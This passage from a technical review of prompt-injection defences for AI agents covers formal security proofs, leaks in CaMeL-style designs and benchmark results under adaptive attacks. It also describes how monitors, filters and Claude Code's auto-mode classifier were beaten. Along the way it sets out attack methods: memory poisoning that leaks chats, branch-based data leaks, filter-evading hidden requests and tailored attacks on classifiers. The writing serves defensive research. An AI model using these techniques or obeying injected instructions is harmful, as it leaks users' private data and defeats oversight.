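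This freedom also weakens the definition. Suppose the plan lets a stranger guess a PIN once and replies only "right" or "wrong". If an injection makes the agent send the whole PIN, the agent still counts as relatively secure, because for any two PINs, some guess would get different replies. A stricter version, uniform relative security, rejects this case because it requires the reference agent's input to be chosen without knowing the secrets.

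### The fence theorem

A fence is a rule that takes tools away from the agent when it reads untrusted text. Let C be the set of tools that the monitor currently allows, and R the set of tools to revoke. At the first untrusted read, the monitor changes

C to C \ R,

which means that it removes every tool in R. Dongol proves that the agent is then relatively secure for every plan, provided that injected instructions can call only tools in R and that nothing ever puts those tools back into C. The result holds whatever text the model mistakes for an instruction. It also satisfies the uniform version of the definition.

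The proof compares the two agents step by step. Before the first untrusted read, there is no injected instruction to obey, so they behave identically. After that read, the monitor denies every injected call. A denial changes neither the monitor's state nor anything the attacker can see, so the reference agent can wait during that step. All other steps come from the plan, and both agents take them under the same monitor state. The attacker therefore sees the same messages from both.

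Isabelle, a program that checks proofs, verified all of this, so any doubts are about how well the theorem's conditions match a real agent:

- Each injected instruction leads to a single tool call. An injected program with several steps could overwrite a variable that the plan later sends. To stop this, the system would have to run such programs in a sandbox that discards their changes, and the fence would have to cover reads as well as calls.
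- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. A real model could look at a secret, or at the monitor's last refusal, before deciding whether to obey.
- The attacker sees the contents and order of messages but not their timing, and never sees a refusal.
- Trusted code runs the plan, and every tool call and untrusted read goes through the monitor.
- A call returns only whether the monitor allowed it, and outside text arrives through separate reads. This excludes a search engine run by the attacker, who could choose the results after seeing the query.

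An assistant that handles successive requests eventually needs its tools back. Returning them with the user's next request isn't safe, because the old email is still in the model's context. Dongol proves that returning them at the start of a fresh model session is safe, if the model can't go on obeying injected calls forever. But the session has to be completely fresh. In an attack on ChatGPT that Johann Rehberger reported in 2024, a document planted an instruction in the assistant's long-term memory, and later conversations loaded it and leaked the user's messages through image links. A fence stops this attack only if it also treats loading the memory as an untrusted read.

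The theorem would cover the GitHub connector in Willison's example, which could publish private code after reading a public bug report. The fence would revoke the tool that proposes public code changes as soon as the agent read a report, so the agent couldn't propose a genuine fix either.

### Where to put the fence

Relative security comes from research on speculative execution, in which a processor runs instructions early on a guess and may leak data if the guess is wrong. A barrier just before the leaking instruction is enough to prevent the leak. An injection is different because it adds its own call, which the model can make at any time after reading the injected text.

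Dongol compares three plans that raise the fence themselves, with a lock command that disables every tool except reading the inbox:

| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected call can leak |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read the email, read a secret, lock | The secret |
| Middle | Read the email, lock, read a secret | Data already in memory, such as from an earlier session |
| Early | Lock before reading the email | Nothing |

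With the middle fence, the agent loses its tools before it reads the secret but after it reads the email. In between, it can still use them, and it may already hold other private data. The automatic fence in the theorem avoids this because the monitor revokes the tools before the email's text reaches the model.

### Approving a tool or an exact call

If a defence blocks an agent from acting after it reads untrusted text, the agent can't answer an email it has just read. User approval can allow the reply, but how safe this is depends on what the user approves.

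Suppose the user approves the reply "See you on Friday". If the approval covers the mail tool rather than that specific message, the monitor allows the next email whatever it contains. An injected instruction can then make the model email private data to the attacker before the plan sends the reply. That email uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks the user's reply. A limit on the number of emails has the same weakness, unless the plan sends its email before it reads anything untrusted.

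If the approval covers the exact arguments of the call, an injected email is sent only if it is identical to the approved one. Dongol proves that this kind of approval is relatively secure against every injection that uses the mail tool, again assuming that the model can't follow injected instructions forever. The proof fails if the attacker can observe timing. An injected order to send private text succeeds only if that text matches the approved reply, which then arrives a step early. The attacker learns only whether the two texts are the same, which will rarely be useful.

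The proof treats the user's approval as trusted, so it doesn't protect a user who approves the outsider's address.

### Corrupted answers in a dual-LLM agent

In the dual-LLM pattern, injected text reaches only a quarantined model, which can't call tools, but the attacker can still corrupt that model's answers. Dongol analyses a plan that reads the user's private notes and an outsider's email, has the quarantined model draft a reply from both, and sends the reply to the outsider. An injection can make the quarantined model quote the notes in the reply, which an honest model wouldn't do, so the agent leaks them to the outsider.

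Labels like CaMeL's stop this by marking anything computed from the notes as private, so the monitor blocks the agent from sending it. The agent is then secure whatever the quarantined model does, but only because it never replies, even when there is no attack. The notes can still leak if the attacker can see the blocked request, for example in an error message.

Labels on data can also miss a leak through a branch. Consider this plan:

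```
answer = ask_quarantined(notes, email)
if answer == 1: send_email(to=outsider, body="1")
else:           send_email(to=outsider, body="0")
```

Both message bodies are constants that the planner wrote, so both are public and pass the check. But an injection can make the quarantined model answer 1 exactly when the notes contain a certain fact, so the outsider can tell from the message whether the fact is there. FIDES guarantees only explicit secrecy, so it would allow this too. CaMeL has a stricter mode that also labels values with the conditions they depend on, which should close the leak. Dongol doesn't analyse that mode. Garby and colleagues found a leak through an untaken branch in CaMeL, which is a good reason to want a proof for the stricter mode.

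An allowlist of web addresses can leak information in a similar way. Suppose the monitor lets the agent fetch only a harmless newsletter. An attacker can inject an instruction to fetch the newsletter if a secret is 0 and a forbidden address otherwise. Anyone who can see whether the newsletter request went out learns whether the secret is 0.

### Checking one plan before it runs

The fence theorem covers every plan but takes away tools that many plans need. CaMeLoT, which Nikolaou and colleagues built on top of CaMeL, instead checks each plan against a set of rules before the agent calls any tool:

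1. The planner writes its program, as in CaMeL.
2. Code turns the program into a finite-state machine, with states for the steps of the plan. The machine includes both branches of every condition, and a loop may repeat or stop after any round.
3. Code marks each value as trusted or tainted. Anything that comes from a quarantined model is tainted.
4. A model checker, which is a program that examines every possible path through the machine, tests each rule. If a rule fails, it returns a path that breaks the rule.
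5. The planner receives that path as feedback and rewrites the plan, up to a fixed number of attempts.

The rules use temporal logic, which can describe the order of events. In the minutes example, one rule could be

AG(call_send_email ⇒ recipient_trusted).

A means "on all paths" and G means "in every state", so the agent must never send an email to an address from an untrusted source. The plan for the minutes breaks this rule with or without an attack, just as it fails under a strict CaMeL policy. But CaMeLoT rejects the plan before the agent runs it.

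The logic can also express requirements about the future, such as "every incident ticket the agent opens must eventually be resolved or escalated". CaMeL's policies can't easily do this because they check one call at a time.

Nikolaou and colleagues could express 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies as rules of this kind. Most of the others depend on facts known only at run time, such as who can currently read a shared file. CaMeL and CaMeLoT made the same decision on 59 of 75 plans, not counting 22 tasks that failed under both because the plan didn't do what the user wanted. Nikolaou and colleagues ran these tasks without injections, so the results measure how closely the two systems agree, not the attack success rate.

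In a second test, based on a security analyst's work, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The paper acknowledges that this comparison is unfair, because the rules were chosen to go beyond what CaMeL can express.

CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's request. A model picks requirements from a fixed list of forms, and ordinary code translates them into logic. On AgentDojo's 97 tasks, the model identified exactly the right set of required actions in 85. In 20 further cases with handwritten plans, the derived rules accepted every correct plan and blocked every bad one. A wrongly derived rule could block a good plan or let a bad one through, and the model checker can't detect that. The model checker's proof is about the state machine, so it applies to the real program only if the state machine represents that program faithfully.

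### What relative security leaves out

A monitor that denies every call makes any agent relatively secure, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't do anything either. The definition doesn't measure whether the agent can still complete its tasks, so, as Dongol points out, that has to be checked separately.

Removing a permission can turn a relatively secure agent into an insecure one. Suppose the plan emails a report to an outsider, as the user intended, and an injection leaks the same report through a web address. The injection discloses nothing new, so the agent counts as relatively secure. If the monitor revokes the mail tool, the reference agent no longer discloses the report, so the same injection counts as a leak. Relative security therefore measures only the disclosure an injection adds, which is little guide to how much the agent discloses overall.

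The three attacks on the minutes show how much this matters:

- Attack 1 is a leak, because the reference agent never sends the salary file. Exact-call approval would stop it and still let the minutes go out.
- Attack 2 counts as secure. The plan takes the address from Bob's email, so the reference agent would also send the minutes to whatever address it found there.
- Attack 3 is out of scope, because a false report to the user reveals nothing to the attacker. The same goes for any hijacking that does damage without leaking data, such as deleting files.

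Agents that choose each call as they go, such as Codex, are out of scope too. They don't fix a plan before their first untrusted read, so there is no reference agent to compare them with.

Garby and colleagues do have a theorem that covers such agents, provided that someone writes them in the paper's own programming language. It applies to every program in that language, including agents that generate code and run it. It is a form of noninterference, adapted to models that answer at random and programs that may never finish. Take two starting states that differ only in data an observer isn't allowed to see, and let μ and ν be the probability distributions of what the observer sees at the end. Then

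Δ(μ, ν) ≤ (div(μ) + div(ν)) / 2,

where Δ is the distance between the distributions, from 0 (identical) to 1, and div is the probability that the program doesn't finish. If the program always finishes, the observer learns nothing about the hidden data. The paper adds that FIDES has a noninterference theorem for one particular agent loop and that CaMeL has no comparable theorem.

Because this is noninterference, useful tasks often need an exception. A second theorem guarantees that the language's endorsement command can't expose secrets, whatever the attacker writes. It doesn't guarantee that the endorsed data is correct, so attack 2 could still succeed if an agent endorsed the outsider's address.

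### Could a learned filter have a guarantee?

Dongol's framework allows a filter, a sanitiser σ that rewrites each untrusted text v before the model reads it. If σ(v) never contains anything the model would treat as an instruction, the agent is relatively secure for every plan and every monitor, even if the attacker can observe timing. This condition assumes that the filter never fails. Code that passes on only a number or a date could meet it. Nobody has a way to prove that a learned filter does, and *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reports that adaptive attacks beat three learned detectors more than 90% of the time.

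The closest thing to a guarantee for a learned filter is erase-and-check, from *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting* (2023). It addresses attackers who disguise a harmful prompt by adding tokens. For tokens added at the end, the procedure removes the last token, then the last two, and so on up to a limit d, and runs the filter on each version. If the attacker added at most d tokens, one of these versions is the original prompt, so if the filter classifies the original as harmful, it will also catch the disguised prompt. The repeated checks take time and raise the chance of a false alarm on a safe prompt. The guarantee helps little against injections, because it covers only prompts that the filter would have caught without the disguise, and the filter would not catch a polite request to change an address.

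Two other papers prove limits on filters. *On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025) uses time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but take a known amount of computation to solve. An attacker hides a harmful request in a puzzle. A model with enough computing time solves the puzzle and obeys the request, while a much faster filter can't tell the prompt from an innocent one. The paper proves that, if secure time-lock puzzles exist, there are models that no such filter can protect. This result is the theoretical counterpart of Red Hat's warning about injections that a small filter can't decode. But the proof uses a model constructed for the purpose, which the paper describes as contrived, and doesn't show that any deployed model behaves this way.

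Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues (2026), in *The Defense Trilemma*, consider a filter D that rewrites prompts. Let f(x) measure how unsafe the model's response to prompt x is, and call x safe if f(x) is below a threshold τ. The paper proves, with a computer-checked proof, that D can't have all three of these properties:

- It rewrites similar prompts in similar ways (continuity).
- It leaves safe prompts unchanged.
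- It makes every prompt safe, so that f(D(x)) < τ for all x.

If the space of prompts is connected, meaning that it doesn't fall into separate pieces, then some series of safe prompts gets closer and closer to a prompt z exactly at the threshold, where f(z) = τ. The filter leaves each of these safe prompts unchanged, so by continuity it must also leave z unchanged, even though z isn't safe.

This result limits real filters less than the paper's title suggests. A prompt exactly at the threshold may be harmless in practice, although Bhatt and colleagues show that, under further assumptions, some clearly unsafe prompts also get through. The result doesn't apply to filters that reject a prompt outright, as most injection classifiers do. Real text also comes in discrete tokens, and for a finite set of prompts the paper proves only that a filter that makes every prompt safe must sometimes turn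 two different prompts into the same one, which is what a sanitiser is meant to do when it deletes an injection from Bob's email.

A more capable filter would still face some of these limits. Ball and colleagues also consider models that cooperate with the attacker, for example by sharing a secret key. Under standard cryptographic assumptions, they prove that no polynomial-time filter, and so no practical one, can then tell the harmful prompts from innocent ones. The proof by Bhatt and colleagues applies to any filter, however capable, that is continuous and leaves safe prompts unchanged. Neither result clearly applies to PromptArmor running on the same model as the agent, because an ordinary model shares no key with attackers and a yes-or-no decision to delete a passage isn't continuous. But Ball and colleagues point out that a filter as powerful as the model raises the question of how to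 align the filter.

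## How the defences hold up when attackers adapt

Tests, unlike proofs, cover only the attacks that someone tried. Let s(D, a) be the success rate of attack a against defence D. A test with one static attack a₀ measures s(D, a₀). An attacker who can try every attack in a set A that includes a₀, and keep the best one, achieves

max s(D, a) over all a in A ≥ s(D, a₀).

The static score is therefore a lower limit on what this attacker can achieve, and readers cannot tell from it how much higher the real figure is.

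Wang and colleagues found that tests of defences lagged behind research on attacks. Of the 37 attack papers they collected by October 2025, 14 used automated optimisation to write the attack, but most evaluations of defences still relied on hand-written templates. A developer's own adaptive test helps but may not be enough. Ma and colleagues point out that a 2020 study of image classifiers broke thirteen defences that had already been through adaptive tests.

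### Twelve broken defences

In *The Attacker Moves Second* (October 2025), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues tried to break 12 defences, two against jailbreaks and ten against prompt injection. They chose from gradient-based optimisation, reinforcement learning, automated search and human attackers, using whichever they thought most likely to work against each defence. The table shows nine of the ten prompt injection defences.

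| Defence | How it works | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks untrusted text | Above 95% |
| Prompt sandwiching | Repeats the user's request | Above 95% |
| StruQ | Trains the model | 100% |
| Meta SecAlign | Trains the model | 96% |
| ProtectAI's classifier | Classifies text | Above 90% |
| Prompt Guard | Classifies text | Above 90% |
| Google's Model Armor | Classifies text | Above 90% |
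| PIGuard | Classifies text | 71% |
| MELON | Reruns the agent without the user's request | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knew the design |

The tenth defence, DataSentinel, failed in every case. By contrast, static attacks on AgentDojo had succeeded as little as 1% of the time against the two prompting defences and 2% of the time against Meta SecAlign.

The rates in the table don't show which defence is strongest, because Nasr and colleagues used different benchmarks for different defences. In the StruQ test, for example, the attacker only had to make the model output a set phrase. The attackers also had far more resources than most criminals would, including plenty of computing power and, for the automated attack on the classifiers, access to each classifier's confidence score. The results show that a skilled and well-funded attacker can break these defences, but not how often an ordinary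 attacker would.

People did even better than the automated attacks. In a red-teaming competition, more than 500 participants collectively broke every scenario in a selected set, while automated search succeeded 69% of the time. Collective success is easier because only one person has to succeed in each scenario, but a widely used agent also faces many attackers at once.

None of the 12 defences restricts permissions or data flow as CaMeL and Progent do. MELON comes closest because it checks tool calls, but whether it detects an attack depends on how a model behaves when it reads the attacker's text. We can't infer from these results how well CaMeL-type designs would resist the same attackers.

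### AutoDojo

Ma and colleagues used AutoDojo to test component-level and system-level defences against the same adaptive attacker. A language model revises the injected text over six rounds. After each round, it receives only the number of cases in which the latest version succeeded. It isn't told which defence the agent has or what the user asked for, and each text has to work for all the user requests that lead the agent to the same document. This attacker is much weaker than the ones Nasr and colleagues used, so a defence that fails against it is weak, but one that withstands it could still fail against a stronger attacker.

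The main tests used five models on AgentDojo's banking, Slack and travel suites, which together have 57 user tasks and 389 security cases. Ma and colleagues left out the workspace suite because in about half of its cases the agent completed neither the user's task nor the attacker's. The results therefore don't cover the setting closest to the office assistant with the March minutes.

These are the results with GPT-4o-mini:

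| Class | Defence | Clean utility | Static attack success | Adaptive attack success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | – | 66.7% | 58.6% | 52.4% |
| Prompt | Reminder | 68.4% | 39.3% | 40.4% |
| Prompt | Spotlighting | 59.6% | 51.7% | 46.8% |
| Filter | Prompt Guard | 63.2% | 54.2% | 49.4% |
| Filter | PIGuard | 43.9% | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| Filter | ProtectAI | 47.4% | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| Filter | DataFilter | 64.9% | 12.6% | 33.4% |
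| System | Progent | 63.2% | 8.2% | 7.7% |
| System | DRIFT | 49.1% | 2.6% | 6.4% |
| System | CaMeL | 26.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| System | ROPE | 59.6% | 6.4% | 4.4% |

PIGuard stopped every static attack but let through 28.0% of the adaptive ones. Most of those were in the banking suite, where the attacker succeeded in 56.3% of cases, compared with 67.4% with no defence. PIGuard also lowered clean utility by 23 percentage points, because it deletes harmless sentences that the agent needs. DataFilter kept nearly all utility, but its attack success rate nearly tripled when the attacker adapted. The two prompt defences and Prompt Guard did little against static or adaptive attacks.

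The paper's opening comparison covers five defences with low attack success rates against static attacks, and only Progent held up against adaptive ones. The full results show that CaMeL and ROPE also held up. CaMeL was the most secure, but it completed only 15 of the 57 clean tasks, compared with 38 for the undefended agent. The attack success rate against DRIFT more than doubled, and Ma and colleagues note that adaptive attacks are generally more successful when a learned model makes decisions while the agent runs.

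Progent and ROPE offered the best balance. The agent completed two fewer clean tasks with Progent than with no defence, and four fewer with ROPE. The drop was larger with DeepSeek-v4-Flash, which completed 51 tasks without a defence, 45 with Progent and 42 with ROPE. Some of the researchers behind ROPE also worked on AutoDojo, so an independent test of ROPE would be valuable.

### How firm Progent's result is

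The adaptive attack did slightly worse than the static one against Progent because a benchmark rule requires AutoDojo to return a newly written text, even when an old one worked better. A real attacker would use whichever text worked better. If we take the better of the two attacks in each suite, Progent's attack success rate is 10.0% (39 of 389 cases).

To save money, Ma and colleagues also let the attacker practise against a version of Progent in which a cheaper model wrote the policies, then used GPT-4o to write them for the final test. An attacker who practised on the real configuration might do better, so they describe their figures for Progent and DRIFT as lower bounds. They ran each test only once, so differences of a few percentage points mean little.

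More rounds of revision helped the attacker only slightly against PIGuard, raising the success rate from 26.0% after two rounds to 30.8% after twelve. Giving the attacker PIGuard's scores and the reasons for each failure lowered the rate from 28.0% to 23.4%, because the attacker's model then concentrated on getting past the filter and its texts became less persuasive to the agent. Nasr and colleagues reached 71% against the same filter, so other attackers can do better than AutoDojo.

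### Requests that leave the decision to the text

An attack is more likely to work when the user's request leaves more to outside content. Ma and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's tasks into three groups:

- In a fully specified task, the request contains everything the agent needs, such as a new home address to enter in the user's account.
- In a param-open task, such as sending the minutes to the address in Bob's email, the user leaves only a value to outside content.
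- In an action-open task, the user leaves the action itself to outside content, as in "do everything on my to-do list".

Against undefended Gemini 2.5 Flash in the banking suite, the adaptive attack succeeded in 66.7% of action-open cases, 23.2% of param-open cases and 13.9% of fully specified cases. The first figure is 6 of 9 cases, all from one task in which the user tells the agent to follow the instructions in a landlord's notice. Across all three suites, the rates followed the same order, at 62.5%, 36.6% and 26.0%, but only four tasks were action-open.

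The next table shows how the defences did against the adaptive attack with GPT-4o-mini.

| Defence | Action-open | Param-open | Fully specified |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 79.2% | 60.5% | 32.3% |
| PIGuard | 54.2% | 31.1% | 17.3% |
| ProtectAI | 45.8% | 18.5% | 3.9% |
| DataFilter | 54.2% | 38.2% | 20.5% |
| Progent | 8.3% | 10.1% | 3.1% |
| DRIFT | 4.2% | 8.0% | 3.9% |
| ROPE | 8.3% | 4.6% | 3.1% |

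On an action-open task, the attacker can write text that looks like ordinary document content, so a filter has nothing to detect. ProtectAI's classifier worked well on fully specified tasks but let through almost half of the attacks on action-open ones.

The system-level defences kept all three rates low, partly because Progent and DRIFT often allow only read-only tools when the request doesn't name an action. The attack then fails, but the agent probably can't carry out the to-do list either.

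The pattern is less consistent on AgentDyn, which has 12 action-open tasks. Fully specified tasks were again the safest overall. But with undefended Gemini 2.5 Flash, param-open tasks were more vulnerable than action-open ones (65.5% against 52.6%), and in the suite of everyday errands there was no clear order. We can therefore be fairly confident that a precise request protects the user, but not that an action-open request is always the most dangerous.

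### Longer tasks with helpful instructions

AgentDyn's tasks average 7.1 steps, twice as many as AgentDojo's, and each includes a helpful instruction from a third party that the agent has to follow. *AgentDyn* compares ten defences on them. These are some of the results with GPT-4o, except for Meta SecAlign, which is itself a model that Meta fine-tuned from Llama 3.3 70B:

| Defence | Clean utility | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
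|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 63.3% | 56.1% | 31.2% |
| Prompt Guard 2 | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| PIGuard | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| ProtectAI | 0.0% | 0.6% | 0.9% |
| Meta SecAlign | 55.0% | 53.4% | 9.0% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

PIGuard and ProtectAI's classifier could not distinguish helpful instructions from malicious ones, so the agent could complete almost no tasks. Prompt Guard 2 let helpful instructions through, but in this test it discarded the whole tool result whenever it detected an injection, so utility fell to 20.8% under attack. Progent had trouble assigning the right permissions among so many tools, and by the later steps of a task it had often blocked almost everything useful.

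Meta SecAlign had the best balance of utility and security, and *AgentDyn* suggests that training the model could be a more practical defence than the others. But the attacks in *AgentDyn* were static. Using adaptive attacks, Nasr and colleagues raised the attack success rate against the same model from 2% to 96% on AgentDojo. Meta SecAlign's result on *AgentDyn* therefore shows that training can preserve utility on difficult tasks, but it provides little evidence about the model's security.

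When Ma and colleagues ran their adaptive attacker on AgentDyn, Progent did worse than it had on AgentDojo. With GPT-4o-mini, the adaptive attack succeeded in 12.7% of cases and the static attack in 15.2%, while the agent completed 6.7% of clean tasks. In the suite of everyday errands, the adaptive attack succeeded in 28.5% of cases and the static attack in 31.0%. A policy can therefore block the user's tasks and still let attacks through, if the model that writes it permits the wrong tools. ROPE again did much better. The agent completed 43.3% of clean tasks, and the adaptive attack succeeded in 2.9% of cases.

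### An independent test of Progent

Narisetty and colleagues ran Progent with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model, as both the agent and the policy writer. They wrote one adaptive attack by hand and aimed it at Progent's most vulnerable part, the model that updates the policy.

| Suite | No defence, static attack | Progent, static attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
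| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adaptive attack did no better than the static one. This is weak evidence that Progent resists adaptive attackers, as Narisetty and colleagues acknowledge. They tried a single template and didn't optimise it. They worded it to make the malicious call look routine to the policy writer, but this probably also made the agent less likely to obey. The attack's low success rate could therefore be due to its poor design.

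The test was also small, with only eight user tasks per suite. Three repetitions gave similar results, but they used the same tasks, so they show only that the measurement is stable. The workspace suite lowers all three means because the model ignored every injection there, even without a defence. Across the other two suites, the means are 38.7%, 6.4% and 4.0%. With this small model, Progent also reduced utility under the static attack from 45.2% to 27.1% and required about 15 times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools of this type.

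Narisetty and colleagues left open, for future work, whether an attack could succeed using only actions the agent is already authorised to take.

### Attacks inside the permitted actions

*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) presents an Amazon benchmark of 90 cases in which the attacker tampers with the user's own task instead of adding another one. For example, the user asks the agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to take the refund amount from the platform's order record. The record authorises $899.99, but the buyer's evidence puts the refund at $1,074.99. The agent has to issue a refund either way, so a rule about which tools it may use can't stop the attack.

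This is attack 2 in a different setting. Unlike in attack 2, the user has named the record that determines the right answer, so a careful agent can always find it. The table gives averages over five models, including Claude Sonnet 4.5 and GLM-5.

| Defence | Ordinary tasks completed | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| None | 95.3% | 17.0% |
| Spotlighting | 98.7% | 15.6% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 98.5% | 10.4% |
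| DRIFT's isolator only | 98.0% | 6.6% |
| Full DRIFT | 88.9% | 7.0% |
| Progent | 74.9% | 15.4% |
| CaMeL | 13.3% | 1.3% |

Progent hardly reduced attack success, although it blocked enough legitimate actions to lower utility by about 20 percentage points. It blocked 5 of the 64 harmful calls that GLM-5 proposed and 3 of the 52 that Claude Sonnet 4.5 proposed. Amounts and recipients often depend on what the agent reads during the task, so a policy that the model writes in advance usually can't specify them.

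CaMeL stopped nearly all of the attacks because it checks where each value came from. But with the policies and labels Zhang and colleagues wrote for it, the agent could complete few of the tasks. Better policies might let it complete more.

DRIFT's isolator, a model that removes suspicious text from tool results, did surprisingly well for a learned component. Planted text that stated a goal, such as a demand for a particular refund, succeeded 2.4% of the time, compared with 12.1% for text that misstated a fact, such as the refund already authorised. The difference fits the general weakness of filters against false information. DRIFT's plan and checklist did not reduce attack success further, because a tampered call still fits the plan.

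Zhang and colleagues also rewrote the attacks to evade a separate detector, and planted goals remained among the easiest to catch. But they didn't optimise any attack against the defences themselves, so an attacker who did might achieve more than these figures suggest.

The results for Progent in AutoDojo and this benchmark are consistent. Most of AutoDojo's attacks need a call that the user's task doesn't, and a permission rule can block that call however the attacker words the text. To stop an attack that only changes a value in a legitimate call, the rule must also restrict that value, which Progent's automatically written policies rarely did.

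A defence's effectiveness also depends on what its monitor can observe of the agent's actions. *INFUSE* (2026) tests Progent and a CaMeL-style control on an agent that writes free-form shell commands instead of calling named tools. With 200 cases per configuration, neither control produced a measurable security gain, while a model-level defence did. The paper limits this conclusion to its own adaptations of the two systems, but results with AgentDojo's neatly defined tools may not carry over to coding agents.

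### Do better models close the gap?

AutoDojo's results vary more between models than between most defences. The table shows attack success rates on AgentDojo.

| Model | No defence, static | No defence, adaptive | PIGuard, adaptive | Progent, adaptive |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 58.6% | 52.4% | 28.0% | 7.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 50.4% | 34.7% | 4.6% | 3.6% |
| DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 22.6% | 16.5% | 10.5% | 4.6% |
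| GPT-5.4-mini | 6.9% | 8.7% | 5.1% | 1.5% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.3% | 1.8% | 0.8% | 0.5% |

*AgentDyn* notes that developers have probably trained many newer models on AgentDojo's standard injection, so a static rate could be low partly because that wording was in the training data. That can't be the whole explanation, because new wording raised Haiku's rate only to 1.8%.

An elaborate defence adds less security when the model already resists most attacks. On GPT-5.4-mini, a one-sentence reminder before each tool result reduced adaptive attack success from 8.7% to 2.1%. Clean utility was 80.7% with the reminder and 77.2% without a defence. Progent, which enforces permission rules, reduced attack success to 1.5%, a difference of two cases out of 389, with a clean utility of 73.7%. The reminder did nearly as well as Progent against a modest attacker. This doesn't make it as safe as a permission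 rule, since Nasr and colleagues beat a similar prompt defence more than 95% of the time with stronger attacks.

A filter can make a strong model much less useful and still let some adaptive attacks through. DeepSeek-v4-Pro completed 89.5% of clean tasks without a defence and 54.4% with PIGuard. With PIGuard in place, the adaptive attack succeeded in 8.2% of cases overall and 13.2% in banking. Both rates are higher than the static attack achieved against the undefended model.

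Better models also resist tampering less well than they resist added tasks. In Zhang and colleagues' tests, attacks succeeded 11.1% of the time against undefended Claude Sonnet 4.5 and 12.9% against GLM-5, the two most resistant of the five models. The rates for the other three were between 17% and 23%.

Figures from the leading developers suggest continued progress in 2026:

- Claude Fable 5, released in June, let through 0.41% of adaptive attacks in coding tasks, compared with 2.09% for Claude Opus 4.8, according to a summary of Anthropic's results by Digital Applied (2026).
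- Anthropic reported in the same month that the closely related Claude Mythos 5 had the best result so far on an injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan.
- Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, from September, reports that the model did as well as or better than Claude Opus 5 on every injection test in the document.
- OpenAI's figure for GPT-6 Sol in October was 97.13% robustness to indirect injection, as reported by Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*. If this is the share of attacks that failed, about 1 in 35 succeeded.

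These figures come from different tests, so they can't show which company's model is safest. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) explains that the company's latest models had saturated the commonly used robustness tests, so it trained an automated attacker to find weaknesses that those tests missed. The security company PromptArmor, which shares its name with the sanitiser, sells protection against such attacks. Its benchmark, *FrontierBreach*, reports successful attacks on frontier models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon.

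### Many attempts

A low success rate per attempt is less reassuring if the attacker can keep trying. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in k attempts is

1 − (1 − p)^k.

Injections against Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred, according to Anthropic figures quoted by Narisetty and colleagues. If every attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the rates would be 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. The measured rates are lower, most likely because 4.7% is an average across scenarios, some of which are much harder to attack than others. An attacker who fails in a hard scenario will probably keep failing, whereas an easy one takes only a few attempts.

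The type of task made an even bigger difference for Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026. VentureBeat reports that no attack succeeded in 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface, the attack success rate was 17.8% with one attempt and 78.6% by the 200th. Additional safeguards reduced the 200-attempt rate to 57.1%. Anyone choosing a model for an agent therefore needs results for the kind of work it will do. The results should also cover as many attempts as an attacker could make, since an outsider who knows Bob's address can send him a new email every day.

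A defence that stops every attack in a test may still fail against an attack designed for it. Anthropic commissioned an outside test of Claude Code's auto mode, in which a classifier decides whether commands may run without the user's approval. The testers ran 72 scenarios ten times each, and no attack succeeded. Johann Rehberger then designed an attack specifically for auto mode, and it succeeded in roughly 60 to 80% of a small number of runs (Heaton, 2026, *The safety number that was zero until someone tried*).

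If a test finds no successes in n independent trials, the true success rate is below about 3/n with 95% confidence. The original test found none in 720 trials, which would put the limit at about 0.4%. But those trials were ten runs each of 72 scenarios, and runs of the same scenario are not independent, so the limit is closer to 4%. Both limits apply only to attacks drawn from the same source as those in the test, so neither covers Rehberger's attack.

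## Combining filters and system controls in deployed agents

Companies that sell agents combine learned components with fixed rules. The learned components decide most individual cases, so it is important to know what each product's rules still prevent once an attacker has fooled those components.

### Claude Code

Anthropic's coding agent has an auto mode, which became the default on most individual and team plans in August 2026. According to Anthropic, each action the agent proposes goes through checks in a fixed order:

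1. Code compares the action with the user's allow, ask and deny rules. A match usually settles the matter.
2. Code approves read-only actions and edits inside the project folder, except edits to protected files.
3. A classifier model decides on nearly everything else, mainly shell commands and network operations.
4. If the classifier blocks the action, the agent receives the reason and can try another way. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the program asks the user instead.

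Anthropic warns that instructions in a prompt don't change what the agent is allowed to do, because the program around the model enforces the rules. A deny rule applies in every mode, even one that skips nearly all other checks. If the user only types "don't push" in the conversation, the classifier will normally block a push, but the restriction can be lost when the program summarises the conversation.

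Allow rules can let commands bypass the classifier. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written one for shell commands, and Anthropic found that many of these rules permitted any command or any Python script. Auto mode suspends such broad rules so that the commands reach the classifier.

A second model, the input probe, is a component-level filter that scans tool results for injections and adds a warning before the agent reads them. The classifier is a system-level judge that doesn't receive the tool results. To succeed, an injection has to get past the probe, hijack the agent, and produce a call that looks like something the user wanted.

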